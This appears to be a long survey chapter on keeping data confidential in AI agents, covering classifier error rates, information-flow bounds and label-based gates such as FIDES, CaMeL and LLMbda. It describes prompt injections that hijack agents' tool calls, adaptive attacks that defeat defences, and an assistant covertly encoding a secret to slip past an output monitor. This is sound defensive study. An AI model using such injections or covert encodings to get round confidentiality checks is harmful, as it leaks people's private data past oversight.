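The researchers wrote the clinic's policy themselves. To test models against an outside authority, they used 214 disclosures from court cases under HIPAA, the US health privacy law. The cases come from a larger collection in *PrivaCI-Bench* (Li, Hu and colleagues, 2025), built to test models on privacy law. For each disclosure, the model read a description of the case, along with who sent what to whom, for what purpose and with what consent. It then answered whether HIPAA permits the disclosure, prohibits it or does not apply. This experiment had no gate and tested only the model's judgement.

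The most accurate configuration, GPT-5.4-mini, agreed with the courts on 87.8% of disclosures. But only 20 of the 214 were prohibited, and the model permitted 11 of those. The overall score barely reflects these misses, since a judge that never answered "prohibited" but got everything else right would score 90.7%. With only 20 cases, the 95% confidence interval for the miss rate runs from about 32% to 77%. Even the lower end would be too high for a gate that relied on this judgement alone.

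Li and colleagues had earlier tested older models on these cases and also found that reasoning helped unpredictably. Asking for step-by-step reasoning raised QwQ-32B's accuracy from 70% to 88% but lowered DeepSeek R1's from 89% to 82%. Giving models both the correct facts about the disclosure and the applicable law worked better than any other method the researchers tried, which fits the idea that many mistakes come from missing information.

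### Agreement with human labellers

Other researchers have reported much higher agreement between models and people, often as Cohen's kappa. This statistic corrects for the agreement that two labellers would reach by chance. If pₒ is the share of items on which they agree and pₑ is the share expected by chance, then

$$\kappa = \frac{p_o - p_e}{1 - p_e}$$

A kappa of 1 means perfect agreement, and 0 means agreement no better than chance. Suppose two people each mark 80% of items "low" and 20% "high". They would agree on 0.8² + 0.2² = 68% of items by chance. If they actually agree on 90%, kappa is (0.90 − 0.68)/(1 − 0.68), or about 0.69.

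*Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems* (Ji, Wu and colleagues, 2026) used kappa to test labels for tools instead of documents. Its system, SEAgent, gives each of an agent's tools five labels and uses fixed rules to block certain sequences of tool calls. OpenAI's o1 model and human annotators separately labelled 80 tools from written descriptions. The overall kappa was 0.95. It was 1.00 for what a tool acts on (local files, outside services or physical devices) but only 0.77 for sensitivity. The overall kappa is higher than four of the five kappas for individual labels, probably because pooling labels from different vocabularies lowers the estimate of chance agreement.

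Kappa also doesn't measure how serious the consequences of a disagreement are. The human annotators gave a tool that opens web pages moderate sensitivity, because it could lead a user to a phishing site, but the model gave it low sensitivity. Several of SEAgent's rules apply only to tools of moderate or high sensitivity, so with the model's label they would not stop this tool. Ji and colleagues had people correct the labels before testing SEAgent against attacks. No attack succeeded in those tests, but this doesn't show how well the system would work with uncorrected labels.

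A tool's label can also be based on evidence that a memo like Ana's doesn't have. IBM Research has proposed inferring labels for agents' tools from their source code, configuration and runtime behaviour.

*Dynamic Capability Scoping for Enterprise AI Agents* (Noyan, 2026) used a model to label 600 invented office requests. For each, the model read the company's written policy and chose which of 15 permissions the task needed, such as querying a database or emailing somebody outside the company. A human reviewer then labelled 60 of the requests without seeing the model's choices. Agreement between the reviewer and the model was high, with a kappa of 0.92 over 688 yes-or-no decisions. Their complete sets of permissions matched for only 68% of the 60 requests, which again shows how much stricter exact matching is than scoring each permission separately.

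The model also rated each request as low, medium or high sensitivity, but agreed with the reviewer only 60% of the time. This would give a kappa of 0.4 if the three ratings were equally common. The reviewer re-examined the 24 disagreements and judged the human label right in 17 cases and the model's in six, with one unclear. Many of the problems involved the medium rating, whose boundaries were vague.

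At the clinic, models did well on sensitivity and badly on permitted recipients, but in Noyan's study they did well on permissions and badly on sensitivity. Whether the model had a definition that settled the answer explains these results better than the difference between describing and deciding, which cannot explain both. The clinic's sensitivity tiers had concrete definitions, such as "billing codes, insurance numbers, salary figures", and the permissions in Noyan's study followed from the task and a written policy. Noyan's "medium sensitivity" and the clinic's full list of people who may see a billing statement were not defined as clearly.

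### The case for using models anyway

Human labels contain mistakes too. When Noyan's reviewer rechecked 20 disagreements between his own permission labels and the model's, he attributed ten to human error and eight to the model, and two were unclear. The corrections mostly involved high-risk permissions, where errors matter most. But he was reviewing his own labels, and he could read the model's justification as he decided. He also checked only disagreements, so he missed any mistakes that he and the model shared.

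Some apparent model errors may be cases on which people disagree. *Observational Equivalence of LLM and Human Annotation* (2026) compared 13 models with human annotators. The models matched a third person about 89% of the time when two other people agreed about a text, but 66% of the time when those two disagreed. The clinic's labels came from a single annotator, so we can't tell how many of the lists counted as wrong a second expert would have accepted. This problem doesn't affect the changes between passes, which compare each model only with itself. But nobody asked a person to label the clinic's documents five times, so it is unclear how much steadier a human would be.

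Checking labels by hand also takes a lot of work. Noyan's reviewer checked a tenth of the requests that the model had labelled, and an ordinary company has far more than 600 documents. Without a model, most of them would realistically have no label. Because Privacy Conductor refuses by default, a clinic with no labels would refuse all 259 legitimate requests. With the labels from GPT-5.4-mini's first pass, it would grant 233 of them and wrongly release documents in 11 other cases. Thornton and colleagues do not think this is good enough for unsupervised use, and suggest that a model draft the descriptive fields and a person approve the role list.

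## What a classifier's error rate does to a confidentiality guarantee

The labelling models at the clinic made too many mistakes for anyone to call their labels a guarantee. A much better classifier is harder to judge. Suppose Ana's company has grown and its router now handles 10,000 queries a day, of which 10%, or 1,000, contain something confidential. The classifier flags 99% of the confidential queries, which is its recall, and misses the other 1%, which is its miss rate. The router therefore sends 10 confidential queries to the cloud every day, or 3,650 a year.

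Accuracy counts correct answers on all items, sensitive or not, so it is a much weaker guide to leaks than recall. *ComplianceGate* reports 99.2% accuracy over six labels. A two-label classifier with the same accuracy would make 80 mistakes a day on this traffic. Nothing would leak if all 80 were over-blocks, but recall would be 92% if all were misses. *ComplianceGate* also describes its recall for personal data as near-perfect, but does not state how many test items contained such data.

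Recall alone is not enough to judge a classifier, because one that flags everything reaches 100%. Measured recall also depends on what the test labels count as sensitive. In *Broad and Efficient PII Detection with Unified Labels*, Hsu and Berlin (2026) relabelled two public test collections using one written definition of each kind of identifier. In five categories of one collection, between 59% and 86% of the positive examples were positive only under the original labels. One was a request to bring "YV9022888", which the original labels counted as a passport number although the sentence didn't mention a passport. In the other collection, the original labels had left out many IP addresses inside web links. Hsu and Berlin also compared their own detector with larger ones at a low false-positive rate, using the same detectors with both sets of labels. Theirs had the highest recall in 11 of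 14 comparisons under the new labels and 9 of 14 under the original ones.

### The same record, judged again

The figure of 10 leaks a day assumes one decision per query. An agent may judge the same record many times, for instance whenever it sends a request that includes the record. Suppose it judges the merger memo at 20 steps, with a 1% chance of a miss at each, and a single miss lets the memo out. If the errors are independent, the chance of at least one miss is

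$$1 - 0.99^{20} \approx 18.2\%$$

If the errors coincide, so that the classifier misses the memo at every step or at none, the chance is still 1%. It can never exceed 20%, because the 20 separate chances add up to 20% and any overlap between them only lowers the total. With a miss rate of pᵢ at step i, the general bounds are

$$\max_i p_i \;\le\; \Pr[\text{at least one miss}] \;\le\; \min\left(1, \sum_i p_i\right)$$

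A deterministic classifier that reads identical text 20 times gives the same answer every time, so the risk stays at 1%. If the assistant rewords the memo between steps, or the conversation around it changes, the errors become partly independent and the risk may rise towards 18%. The clinic's models changed their labels even on unchanged documents.

Adding a second classifier reverses the arithmetic, because now the memo gets out only if both miss it.

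| Set-up, with a 1% miss rate per check | Errors coincide | Errors independent | Highest possible |
|---|---|---|---|
| 20 checks, and one miss releases the record | 1% | 18.2% | 20% |
| Two checks, and only a double miss releases it | 1% | 0.01% | 1% |

Assuming that the classifiers fail independently gives a result close to the worst case in the top row, but in the bottom row it makes the system look a hundred times safer than it might be. So anyone who multiplies the miss rates of stacked classifiers needs evidence that the classifiers fail on different items.

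The evidence from language models used as judges points the other way. Kohli (2026), in *Nine Judges, Two Effective Votes*, gave nine models from seven families 1,000 pairs of sentences and asked whether one followed from the other, contradicted it or did neither. Each model disagreed with the majority of 100 human annotators on 28% to 36% of the pairs. All nine were wrong on 51 pairs, where independent errors would have produced fewer than one. The average correlation φ between two models' errors was 0.39, and the standard formula for the number of independent votes in a panel of k then gives

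$$n_{\text{eff}} = \frac{k}{1 + (k-1)\varphi} = \frac{9}{1 + 8 \times 0.39} \approx 2.2$$

*Agreement Overstates Evidence* (Hossain, Yousefi and Lim, 2026) found a lower average correlation of 0.21 among ten judges, which made them equivalent to about 3.5 independent ones. The correlation was stronger among the most accurate models, even when they came from different providers.

These experiments did not involve judging confidentiality, and some of the sentence pairs were probably ambiguous, so the figures may not carry over, but they allow a rough estimate. Two classifiers with the same miss rate p and error correlation φ both miss an item with probability p² + φp(1 − p). For p = 1% and φ = 0.39, this is about 0.4%. Adding the second classifier would therefore cut the company's 10 leaks a day to about four, compared with one every ten days if the classifiers' errors were independent.

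### What a clean test can establish

So far the 1% has been a known quantity. In practice somebody estimates it from a test, and the best possible result is no misses at all. If the true miss rate is p, a classifier gets through n independent sensitive items without a miss with probability (1 − p)ⁿ. The 95% upper bound is the rate at which that probability falls to 5%:

$$(1-p)^n = 0.05 \quad\Rightarrow\quad p = 1 - 0.05^{1/n} \approx \frac{3}{n}$$

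For 600 sensitive items the bound is about 0.5%, so a classifier with a perfect score could still leak five items a day at Ana's company. Only sensitive items count toward n, because a harmless query cannot produce a miss. If the 600 items had the same mix as the company's traffic, only 60 would be sensitive and the bound would be 4.9%. Sixty near-copies of one template would provide even weaker evidence.

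Getting the bound below 0.1% takes 2,995 sensitive items without a miss. Showing that the company should expect less than one leak a year would take about 1.1 million. Kaur (2026), in *What AI Red-Team Evaluations Can and Cannot Prove*, calculates how weak the evidence from a clean result is when failures are rare. A run of 520 trials without a failure is 0.77 times as probable if the true failure rate is 0.1% as it is if the rate is 0.05%, so it is only weak evidence for the lower rate.

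Kaur does not dismiss such tests. If a classifier fails 1% of the time, it has less than a 5% chance of getting through 299 trials without a failure. Testing works well for a company that mainly wants to know whether a classifier misses one query in 50 or one in 500. But Kaur sets conditions besides size. The test items must also resemble what the system will handle in use, and adding more unrepresentative items does not help with that.

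### Honest mistakes and chosen inputs

When Ana pastes the memo into the assistant, she is not trying to get it past the router. Her wording is unrelated to the classifier's weak spots, so the miss rate on similar documents is a fair estimate of her risk. That estimate can still go out of date. If all the test documents predate the Northwind deal, the classifier may do worse on documents about mergers.

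If 0.5% of possible wordings get through, Ana will use one by accident about once in 200 attempts, but an attacker who can write some of the content needs to find only one and can then reuse it. Blind guessing at independent wordings would give the attacker an even chance of success after 139 attempts, and an attacker who learns from each refusal needs fewer. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) found that attackers who adapted to a defence could get past most of the recent jailbreak and prompt injection defences it studied, including some with reported attack success rates near zero.

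Sensitivity classifiers have a different task, and an attacker cannot always choose the text they label. For example, a competitor who wants the merger memo did not write it. The danger is that a prompt injection might lead the assistant to disguise the memo's contents before sending them. *LLM Censorship* (2023) proves that no classifier, however good, can determine from an output alone whether it is permissible text or a reversible encoding of forbidden text. If the attacker and the assistant share a code in which "soup" means Northwind, a message that appears to be about lunch can refer to the company.

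*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* sets the aim of blocking prohibited flows whatever their cause, including an attacker, a model's mistake or a model with the wrong goals. A classifier's miss rate cannot meet this standard because it describes only one cause and one kind of input. Kolluri and colleagues similarly distinguish probabilistic defences, in which they include classifiers, from deterministic ones, which stop every tool call that violates the policy. A deterministic gate placed behind a classifier is still exposed to the classifier's errors because it relies on the classifier's labels. The error rate of those labels can be estimated for honest traffic, but attacker-written content may have no stable error rate to estimate.

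### Two runs and one email

Suppose that a classifier reads the assistant's outgoing emails and never misses one that mentions confidential facts. That would still not give noninterference. Consider the sentence "The lobby will be busy on Thursday" and two versions of the assistant:

```
# Version A
send("dev", "The lobby will be busy on Thursday.")

# Version B
if memo.signing_day == "Thursday":
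    send("dev", "The lobby will be busy on Thursday.")
else:
    send("dev", "The lobby will be quiet on Thursday.")
```

Version A sends the same email whatever the memo contains, so it satisfies noninterference. Version B tells Dev whether the signing is on Thursday. If it is, both versions send the same email. A classifier that reads the email must give the same verdict on both versions, and that verdict is wrong for one of them. Letting the classifier read the memo too does not help, because the memo is the same in both cases. The versions differ only in what they would have sent if the memo had been different, and the classifier cannot read that email because it was never written.

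*Hyperproperties* (Clarkson and Schneider, 2009) puts this in general terms, using "trace" for the record of one execution. A rule such as "never write to the network after reading a file" is a property of single traces, so a monitor can detect a violation by watching one run. Noninterference is a hyperproperty, meaning a property of the whole set of traces a system can produce. A violation of one strict version of noninterference always consists of two traces that at first look the same to a low-clearance observer and later look different.

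This suggests that comparing the assistant's results with those of a copy given a different memo would be a better test than reading emails. Clarkson and Schneider show that checking runs in pairs can turn such a hyperproperty into an ordinary property of the two copies together, which existing proof methods can handle. This may lead to a proof for a program with source code, but for an assistant built on a language model it is mostly a way to find leaks such as the one in version B.

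Another of their examples matters for anyone who updates a model. A system outputs 0, 1 or a secret bit, choosing freely among the three. The set of possible outputs is {0, 1} whatever the secret is, so the system satisfies a policy that requires only that this set not depend on the secret. A replacement that always takes the third option does nothing the old system could not have done, but it reveals the secret every time. An assistant that varies its wording at random could start revealing secrets in the same way if someone turned the randomness off.

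By this argument, if a gate reads only the output and lets Dev observe at least two different outcomes (two different sentences, say, or an email and no email), some version of the assistant can use them to signal one bit about the memo. A label gate does better because the label records what the assistant read before it wrote. Version A never opened the memo, so its email can go to Dev. Both of version B's possible emails carry the memo's label, so the gate stops both.

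### Bounding how often the classifier is wrong

An organisation that cannot achieve noninterference may still want a stronger guarantee than a test score. Conformal methods choose the classifier's threshold so that its error rate has a proven bound. *Conformal Prediction Adaptive to Unknown Subpopulation Shifts* (2025) sets a lower bound on recall by calibrating only on positive items. Its positives are false answers from a language model, but the same method would work for sensitive documents.

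Suppose the company collects 999 sensitive documents that the classifier has not seen in training, has it score each for sensitivity, and sorts the scores. It sets the threshold at the tenth lowest and flags any document that scores at least that much. When a new sensitive document arrives, there are 1,000 in all, and the new one is equally likely to hold any place in the order. The classifier misses it only if it is among the lowest ten, so

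$$\Pr[\text{miss}] \le \frac{10}{1000} = 1\%$$

The argument holds however bad the classifier is, but a bad one needs a threshold so low that it flags almost everything. The argument assumes exchangeability, meaning that the new document could have swapped places with any of the 999 without changing the probabilities. *Do I Need the Cloud?* (2026), which describes a router for the separate steps of an agent's task, explains why its method has no such bound. The method adjusts the router's confidence scores so that they are right on average, which is a weaker property, and the paper has not checked that successive steps are exchangeable. They may well not be, since each step depends on the ones before it.

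The 1% is an average over possible calibration sets as well as new documents. *RACER* (2026), which applies the idea to choosing among language models, takes its expectation over both. A company with an unlucky set of 999 documents could have a true miss rate above 1% for as long as it uses that threshold.

Uddin and Bauer (2026), in *Conformal LLM Routing with Distribution-Free Safety Guarantees*, aim for a bound that deals with bad luck in calibration. Their router sends easy questions to a cheap model. They call it a violation when the cheap model gets a question wrong that the expensive one would have got right. For a tolerance α and a permitted failure chance δ, they want

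$$\Pr\big[\,\Pr(\text{violation} \mid \text{sent to the cheap model}) > \alpha\,\big] \le \delta$$

The outer probability is over calibration sets. The router uses a threshold at which an upper confidence limit on the violation rate is no more than α. On school mathematics problems, with α at 30% and δ at 10%, it sent 37% of questions to the cheap model and had violations on 28% of those. An ordinary threshold tuned on a validation set sent 60% but exceeded α, with violations on 31.7%. The proof supports the guarantee a little less firmly than the formula suggests, because the method tries many thresholds and takes the lowest that passes, which raises the chance that a bad threshold passes by luck. Uddin and Bauer support this step with a check on their data, and mention a stricter search that would not need the check.

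If "violation" meant "contains something confidential", the same method would limit the share of sensitive queries among those sent to the cloud, which is a different quantity from the miss rate. With 9,000 harmless queries going to the cloud each day, a 1% limit on that share allows about 91 sensitive queries a day, whereas a 1% miss rate allows 10.

Neither bound protects every kind of secret equally. If merger documents make up 0.5% of the company's sensitive queries, the classifier could miss all of them and still stay within a 1% miss rate. An attacker's text is not exchangeable with the calibration set, so neither bound holds under attack. A conformal guarantee is reasonable for a large stream of similar requests, such as customer questions that contain phone numbers, where nobody gains by fooling the classifier and the company can remedy each leak. It is a poor fit for Ana's memo because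 one miss could ruin the deal.

### Bounding how much gets out

Quantitative information flow asks how much an observer learns instead of how often a classifier errs. Smith, in *On the Foundations of Quantitative Information Flow* (2009), measures this by the observer's chance of guessing the secret in one try. Before any output, the best guess about a secret H is its most probable value, and Smith calls that probability the vulnerability V(H). After the observer sees an output L, the average chance of a correct guess is

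$$V(H \mid L) = \sum_{\ell} \max_h \Pr[L=\ell \mid H=h]\,\Pr[H=h]$$

Min-entropy leakage is the growth in this chance, in bits:

$$\text{leakage} = \log_2 \frac{V(H \mid L)}{V(H)}$$

Suppose the memo names one of 16 companies, all equally likely as far as Dev knows, so his chance of guessing the right one is V(H) = 1/16. The gate allows the assistant to send Dev one of three fixed sentences or nothing, which makes four outcomes. No term in the sum above can exceed V(H), so after Dev sees the outcome, his chance of guessing right is at most 4 × 1/16 = 1/4, which is a leak of at most two bits.

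This bound needs no test data and makes no assumption about the model. It holds even if the assistant misunderstands the memo or an attacker controls every choice the assistant makes. The gate only has to enforce the list of outcomes, but the count has to include everything Dev can observe, such as the time of the email.

Smith chose min-entropy leakage because averages can mislead here too. Earlier work mostly used Shannon entropy, which measures average uncertainty. Suppose a gate wrongly releases 1% of all possible 64-bit access keys in full and sends a fixed message for the rest. By the Shannon measure, it leaks about 0.65 bits, which sounds negligible. But an observer can now guess the key 1% of the time, up from one in 2⁶⁴. Min-entropy leakage measures this increase and is about 57 bits, close to the 64 bits that publishing the key would leak.

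Repeated messages use up the allowance, since two days of four-outcome messages give 16 combinations, enough to identify the company. Smith points out that the number of bits leaked in one step does not determine how fast this happens. Asking "is the password g?" and asking "is it at most g?" both count as one bit, but k questions of the first kind can separate only k + 1 cases, while k of the second can separate 2ᵏ. *L3M* (2026), an agent system that meters how much confidential data each agent has read and how much data it has sent, limits the total leak to the smaller of the two amounts. An agent that has read 64 confidential bytes and sent two 50-byte requests has leaked at most 64 bytes, not 100.

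Free text uses up any such allowance immediately. An email of 200 lower-case letters and spaces could carry about 950 bits. *SecureClaw* (2026) reaches a similar result for summaries of protected data. Its main bound on an attacker's ability to tell two secrets apart is the number of summaries multiplied by the most that changing the secret can alter the distribution of one summary. If a summary can copy the secret, that change is at its maximum and the bound guarantees nothing.

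Tight limits also reduce how much useful work agents complete. *MNC* (2026) gave agents a cumulative leakage budget for the messages they exchange. With a budget of 0.5, the agents completed 54.8% of tasks, and the most successful attacker in the tests scored 0.035 for leakage. Doubling the budget raised task completion to 56.7% and the leakage score to 0.048. Doubling it again raised the leakage score to 0.062 without increasing task completion.

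Limiting how many bits can leak makes sense for a secret with many possible values, such as an access key, when the observer needs only a few fixed replies, but it gives little protection to a secret with two values. If Dev thinks a merger is as likely as not, one bit can raise his chance of being right from 50% to 100%.

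## How formal information flow control works in agents without a classifier

If an agent's data arrives with provenance labels, ordinary code can enforce confidentiality without analyzing any text. FIDES, Microsoft's reader-set design, does this and also gives each piece of data an integrity label, which records whether an outsider could have written it. Anything the agent derives from a stranger's email is untrusted, and an agent that has read untrusted text may be following someone else's instructions.

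### One task, step by step

Suppose Ana asks her assistant to send Ben a summary of the merger memo and to tell Dev which rooms are booked on Thursday. In FIDES, a language model called the planner picks each tool call. Its context, meaning the conversation so far, starts out trusted and public. A successful run looks like this, with readers in braces:

```
read_document("merger memo")            -> #memo      {Ana, Ben}
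query_llm("Summarise this.", #memo)     -> #summary   {Ana, Ben}
send_email("ben", #summary)             -> allowed
read_calendar("Thursday")               -> "Room 2"   {everyone}
send_email("dev", "Room 2 is booked.")  -> allowed
```

The first tool returns the memo's text and its label. Because that label is more restrictive than the context's, FIDES stores the text in a variable and shows the planner only the name `#memo`. The planner can't summarise text it hasn't seen, so it passes the variable to a second, isolated model with no tools. FIDES stores that model's answer in another variable, whose label is the join of the context's label and the memo's.

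Just before the third call, FIDES replaces `#summary` with the actual text, and the policy gate compares the recipient with the text's label. The label permits Ben to read the text, so the gate allows the email. The calendar is public, so its contents go directly into the planner's context, and the planner can write to Dev.

In a simpler agent, the memo's text would have entered the context at the first step, and its label would have blocked the email about Room 2.

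Some tasks require the planner to see what is in a variable. The planner can inspect the variable, which raises the context's label, or it can ask the isolated model a question that allows only "yes" or "no". FIDES records this restriction in the label, so a policy can treat a one-bit answer about the memo more leniently than free text. But the label does not record how many answers the planner has received. Joining two yes-or-no labels gives another yes-or-no label, so after ten questions the context could hold ten bits about the memo under a label for a one-bit answer. Costa and colleagues did not test this feature.

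### What explicit secrecy guarantees

FIDES provides explicit secrecy. To define it, take a run of the agent on stored data d₁, and let g be the combined effect on that data of the actions the agent took. Write d₁ =_L d₂ when two sets of stored data have the same public part. Explicit secrecy requires that

$$\text{for all } d_2 =_L d_1: \quad g(d_1) =_L g(d_2)$$

If we replace the memo and replay the same actions, everything public must stay unchanged. Noninterference is stricter because it requires this even when the agent reads the new memo and can choose different actions.

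Suppose the planner has inspected the memo and also holds two public web pages in variables, where FIDES put them because they are untrusted. It forwards one page to Dev if the signing is on Thursday and the other if it isn't. Both pages have public labels, so the gate can let either through, but Dev can tell from which page arrives whether the signing is on Thursday. The definition also leaves out timing, and it assumes that the model always gives the same output for the same input.

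### Attacks stopped and tasks lost

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark of 97 tasks in simulated office, travel, banking and Slack environments, with prompt injections hidden in the data. With GPT-4o as the planner and no policy checks, 152 attacks succeeded against a basic agent and 21 against FIDES. With the checks on, none succeeded against either, so the gate alone was enough to stop the attacks. The variables helped the agent get more work done behind the gate, as the completion rates without attacks show:

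| Agent | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic, no policy checks | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Basic, with policy checks | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, with policy checks | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

FIDES did worst on travel, partly because GPT-4o often misused the variables. With OpenAI's o1 model, it completed 68% of the travel tasks.

The perfect security score depends on labels that were guaranteed to be correct for the attacks tested. AgentDojo has no labels, so the researchers marked a field as untrusted if at least one attack in the benchmark used it. The test therefore shows that the gate works when the labels are correct, but not that anyone could label the data correctly without knowing the attacks. The researchers also hid only untrusted data in variables, so the table does not show how many tasks an agent could complete if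 FIDES hid confidential data too.

*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) tested four recent models on the Slack tasks, and all four resisted every attack even with policies turned off. The researchers then simulated a successful injection by giving part of the agent only the attacker's text as its instructions. Without policies, between 16% and 42% of these injections succeeded, depending on the model. With label checks, all of them failed, so the gate's protection does not depend on the model noticing the attack. The policies also reduced task completion in this test, from between 67% and 76% to between 40% and 48%.

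Kolluri and colleagues argue that such comparisons make the unprotected agent look too good. In practice, agents often ask a person to approve every consequential action, but benchmarks don't count these requests against them. Using o3-mini, they found that an agent without labels completed 24% of AgentDojo's tasks with no human approval. FIDES completed 50%, and their own agent, Prudentia, which plans around the policies, completed 59%. On this measure, labels let the agent do more work alone, because it needs approval only when the gate can't verify that an action is allowed.

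### Writing the program in advance

CaMeL, another agent design, separates planning from reading more strictly than FIDES does. A trusted model writes a program from the user's request alone. An interpreter then runs the program, tracks labels on the values and checks each tool call. A second model, which has no tools, can read documents and return values to the program. The program can branch on those values, but the model that wrote it cannot read a document and then change its plan. FIDES's planner can do this if it accepts a more restrictive context label.

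This separation is not enough without the label checks. In *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) reran CaMeL with the checks off on a task that asked it to read a file and follow the instructions in it. CaMeL wrote a loop with a branch for each tool, which let whoever wrote the file choose the tool calls. Two attacks succeeded this way. The researchers also found that secrets could leak past CaMeL's tracking even with the checks on.

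The checks reduce how many tasks an agent completes. In Zhou and colleagues' tests, CaMeL completed 13 to 17 of the 21 Slack tasks without policies, depending on the model, but only 4 to 6 with them.

### LLMbda and its theorem

LLMbda, by Garby and colleagues, is a small programming language for agents with label tracking built into its definition. Every value has a label, and so does the program's conversation with the model. If a program sends the memo to the model, the conversation takes on the memo's label. The model's reply inherits that label, and so does the result of running any code in the reply. A program can also fork the conversation, ask about the memo in the copy, and then discard the copy. The main conversation stays public, but the answer keeps the memo's label.

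Fenton's example from the 1970s leaked a secret through a variable that one branch changed and the other left alone. In LLMbda, the only thing a program can change in place is the conversation, so a similar leak would look like this:

```
ask("Remember that x is false.")
if memo.deal_is_on: ask("Set x to true.")
ask("What is x?")
```

When the deal is on, LLMbda stops the program at the second line, because a branch that depends on the memo may not write to a public conversation. If LLMbda raised the conversation's label inside the branch instead, the label would rise only when the deal was on. When the deal was off, the conversation would stay public, and so would the answer "false". Stopping the program still reveals whether the deal is on to anyone who can see whether the program finished, because it skips the branch and finishes when the deal is off.

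The theorem about LLMbda allows this one kind of leak, so Garby and colleagues call the property termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference. "Termination-insensitive" means that the secrets may affect whether the program finishes, but nothing else the observer can see. "Probabilistic" means that the theorem compares the probabilities of results, because models sample their replies.

To make this exact, let μ(q) and ν(q) be the probabilities of the public result q under two different memos. Each set of probabilities may add up to less than 1, and the remainder is the chance that the program runs forever or gets stopped. The theorem says that some third set of probabilities, adding up to at most 1, is at least as large as both μ and ν for every result. This is the same as requiring

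$$\sum_q \max\big(\mu(q), \nu(q)\big) \le 1$$

Suppose that under one memo the program returns A 50% of the time, B 30% of the time and no result 20% of the time. Under another memo, the figures are 40%, 50% and 10%. The larger figure for each of A and B is 50%, and these add up to 100%, so the theorem permits the difference. Both sets of figures could come from a program that would return A and B equally often but sometimes gives no result. If the program returned B 60% of the time under the second memo, the total would be 110%, which the theorem rules out.

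The condition also limits how much the results can differ. Half the sum of the differences |μ(q) − ν(q)| is at most the average chance of not finishing, which is 15% in the permitted example. If the program always finishes, the two sets of probabilities must be identical.

Garby and colleagues proved this for every program that LLMbda can express, using Lean, a language for writing proofs that a computer can check. The interpreter that calls the model is also written in Lean, and the proofs cover that code. The theorem assumes nothing about the model's replies, so it holds even if an attacker controls every word of them.

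### Two successful attacks in 1,296 runs

The researchers built an agent called Randori in LLMbda. An agent that writes code usually needs several attempts, and each failed attempt on real data would leave restrictive labels on the conversation. Randori therefore tests its programs on simulated tools and uses the real tools only when a program works.

The evaluation used AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, each paired with nine attacks. Each of three models ran every combination three times, for a total of 1,296 runs, and two attacks succeeded. In about two-thirds of the combinations, a program written for the user's task would never contain the tool calls the attack needs, so writing the program in advance is generally enough to defeat those attacks. Both successful attacks occurred in the 423 runs of the remaining combinations, which are the harder test.

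In both cases, the user had asked the agent to make a payment described in a text file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. Randori's program had used a command called `endorse`, which marks untrusted data as trusted. Without that command, LLMbda blocks the attack, but it would also block the payment if the file were genuine.

With GPT-5.2 and no attacks, Randori completed 75% of its runs, compared with 67% for CaMeL without policy checks and 38% for CaMeL with them. With only 16 tasks, the margins of error are around 20 percentage points, so 75% and 67% are not clearly different. Some of Randori's success depends on `endorse`. Removing it lowered completion from 75% to 63% with one model and from 65% to 54% with another.

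The model that writes the program also decides where to use `endorse`, so the system still depends on a learned judgement despite its formal proof. The damage a wrong decision can do is limited because the model decides before it reads any untrusted data, and a second theorem shows that `endorse` cannot weaken the protection of secrets.

### Labels in existing products

Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes prototypes that add labels to tools that developers already use. Many agents reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to outside servers. The prototypes put labels in the metadata of MCP messages. A server can also publish a policy for each tool. One sample policy looks up the current members of a chat channel before the agent posts a message to it. GitHub Copilot CLI, a command-line coding assistant, has an experimental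 setting that updates a context label after every tool result.

Microsoft illustrates the idea with an office worker, Alex, who asks an agent to handle unanswered emails. One is from Priya and previews the quarterly sales. Another is from Marco, who is curious about the sales but isn't yet allowed to see them. An agent that has read both emails can write only for people who may read both:

$$\{\text{Alex}, \text{Priya}\} \cap \{\text{Alex}, \text{Marco}\} = \{\text{Alex}\}$$

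The agent therefore can't reply to Marco without Alex's approval. If Priya had copied Marco on her email, the result would be {Alex, Marco} and the agent could reply without asking Alex. Nobody is attacking the agent here, and no model has to judge whether sales figures are confidential.

The sample policy for chat messages is looser than this example suggests. It allows a message to go to anyone if the agent has read only trusted data, an exception Kolluri and colleagues also used in their tests. The reasoning is that no outsider could have influenced the agent, so the user must have wanted the message sent. But the agent could have misunderstood the user. If Ana wrote the memo herself and the assistant confuses Dev with Ben, this policy lets the summary go to Dev. Requiring every recipient to be a permitted reader would prevent that, but it would also block some messages Ana wants to send.

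### What has to be right already

All these systems assume that the source labels are correct. Costa and colleagues treat an email's sender and recipients as its readers, though they note that somebody may have shared it more widely. The systems also assume that the tools are neither malicious nor faulty, since no later check will protect salary data that a tool has labeled public.

They also need complete mediation, meaning every route out of the system passes through the gate. The Copilot prototype checks only selected tools from GitHub's server. Agents that operate a web browser are harder to cover. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes et al., 2025) points out that these agents act through clicks and keystrokes, which are too low-level for a sensible policy. A gate that receives only the screen position of a click can't determine whether the click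 sends an email or closes a window.

Labelling takes work, and developers will sometimes forget. In Microsoft's prototype, connecting a server that doesn't supply labels requires a description of each tool's output, a function that computes its labels and a policy. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026), which announces FIDES for the company's agent-building toolkit, Agent Framework, warns that a tool without labels counts as trusted and public. The toolkit's documentation gives a different default, untrusted and public, and says that a forgotten tool therefore "fails closed rather than open". That is true for integrity but not for confidentiality, because if a developer forgets to label a tool that reads personnel files, the gate will treat those files as public.

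A more restrictive default would cause label creep. Agent Framework combines labels by keeping the most restrictive, so one private result can stop an agent from posting anything publicly for the rest of its run. Microsoft suggests, as one option, inferring labels from basic facts about a tool, such as treating everything from a tool that requires a login as private. That is safer, but it would give a canteen menu on the staff website the same label as a confidential merger memo.

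### Data that arrives without a label

Some data has no useful provenance label, even when developers are careful. FIDES normally treats the user's message as trusted and public. If Ana pastes the merger memo into her request, the memo loses its label, as it did with the router, so the gate lets the assistant email the text to Dev.

Old files and web forms cause similar problems. A contract on a shared drive may be open to the whole company only because someone chose the wrong setting years ago. When a customer fills in the comments box on a web form, the system records which box the text came from, but not that the customer described an illness there.

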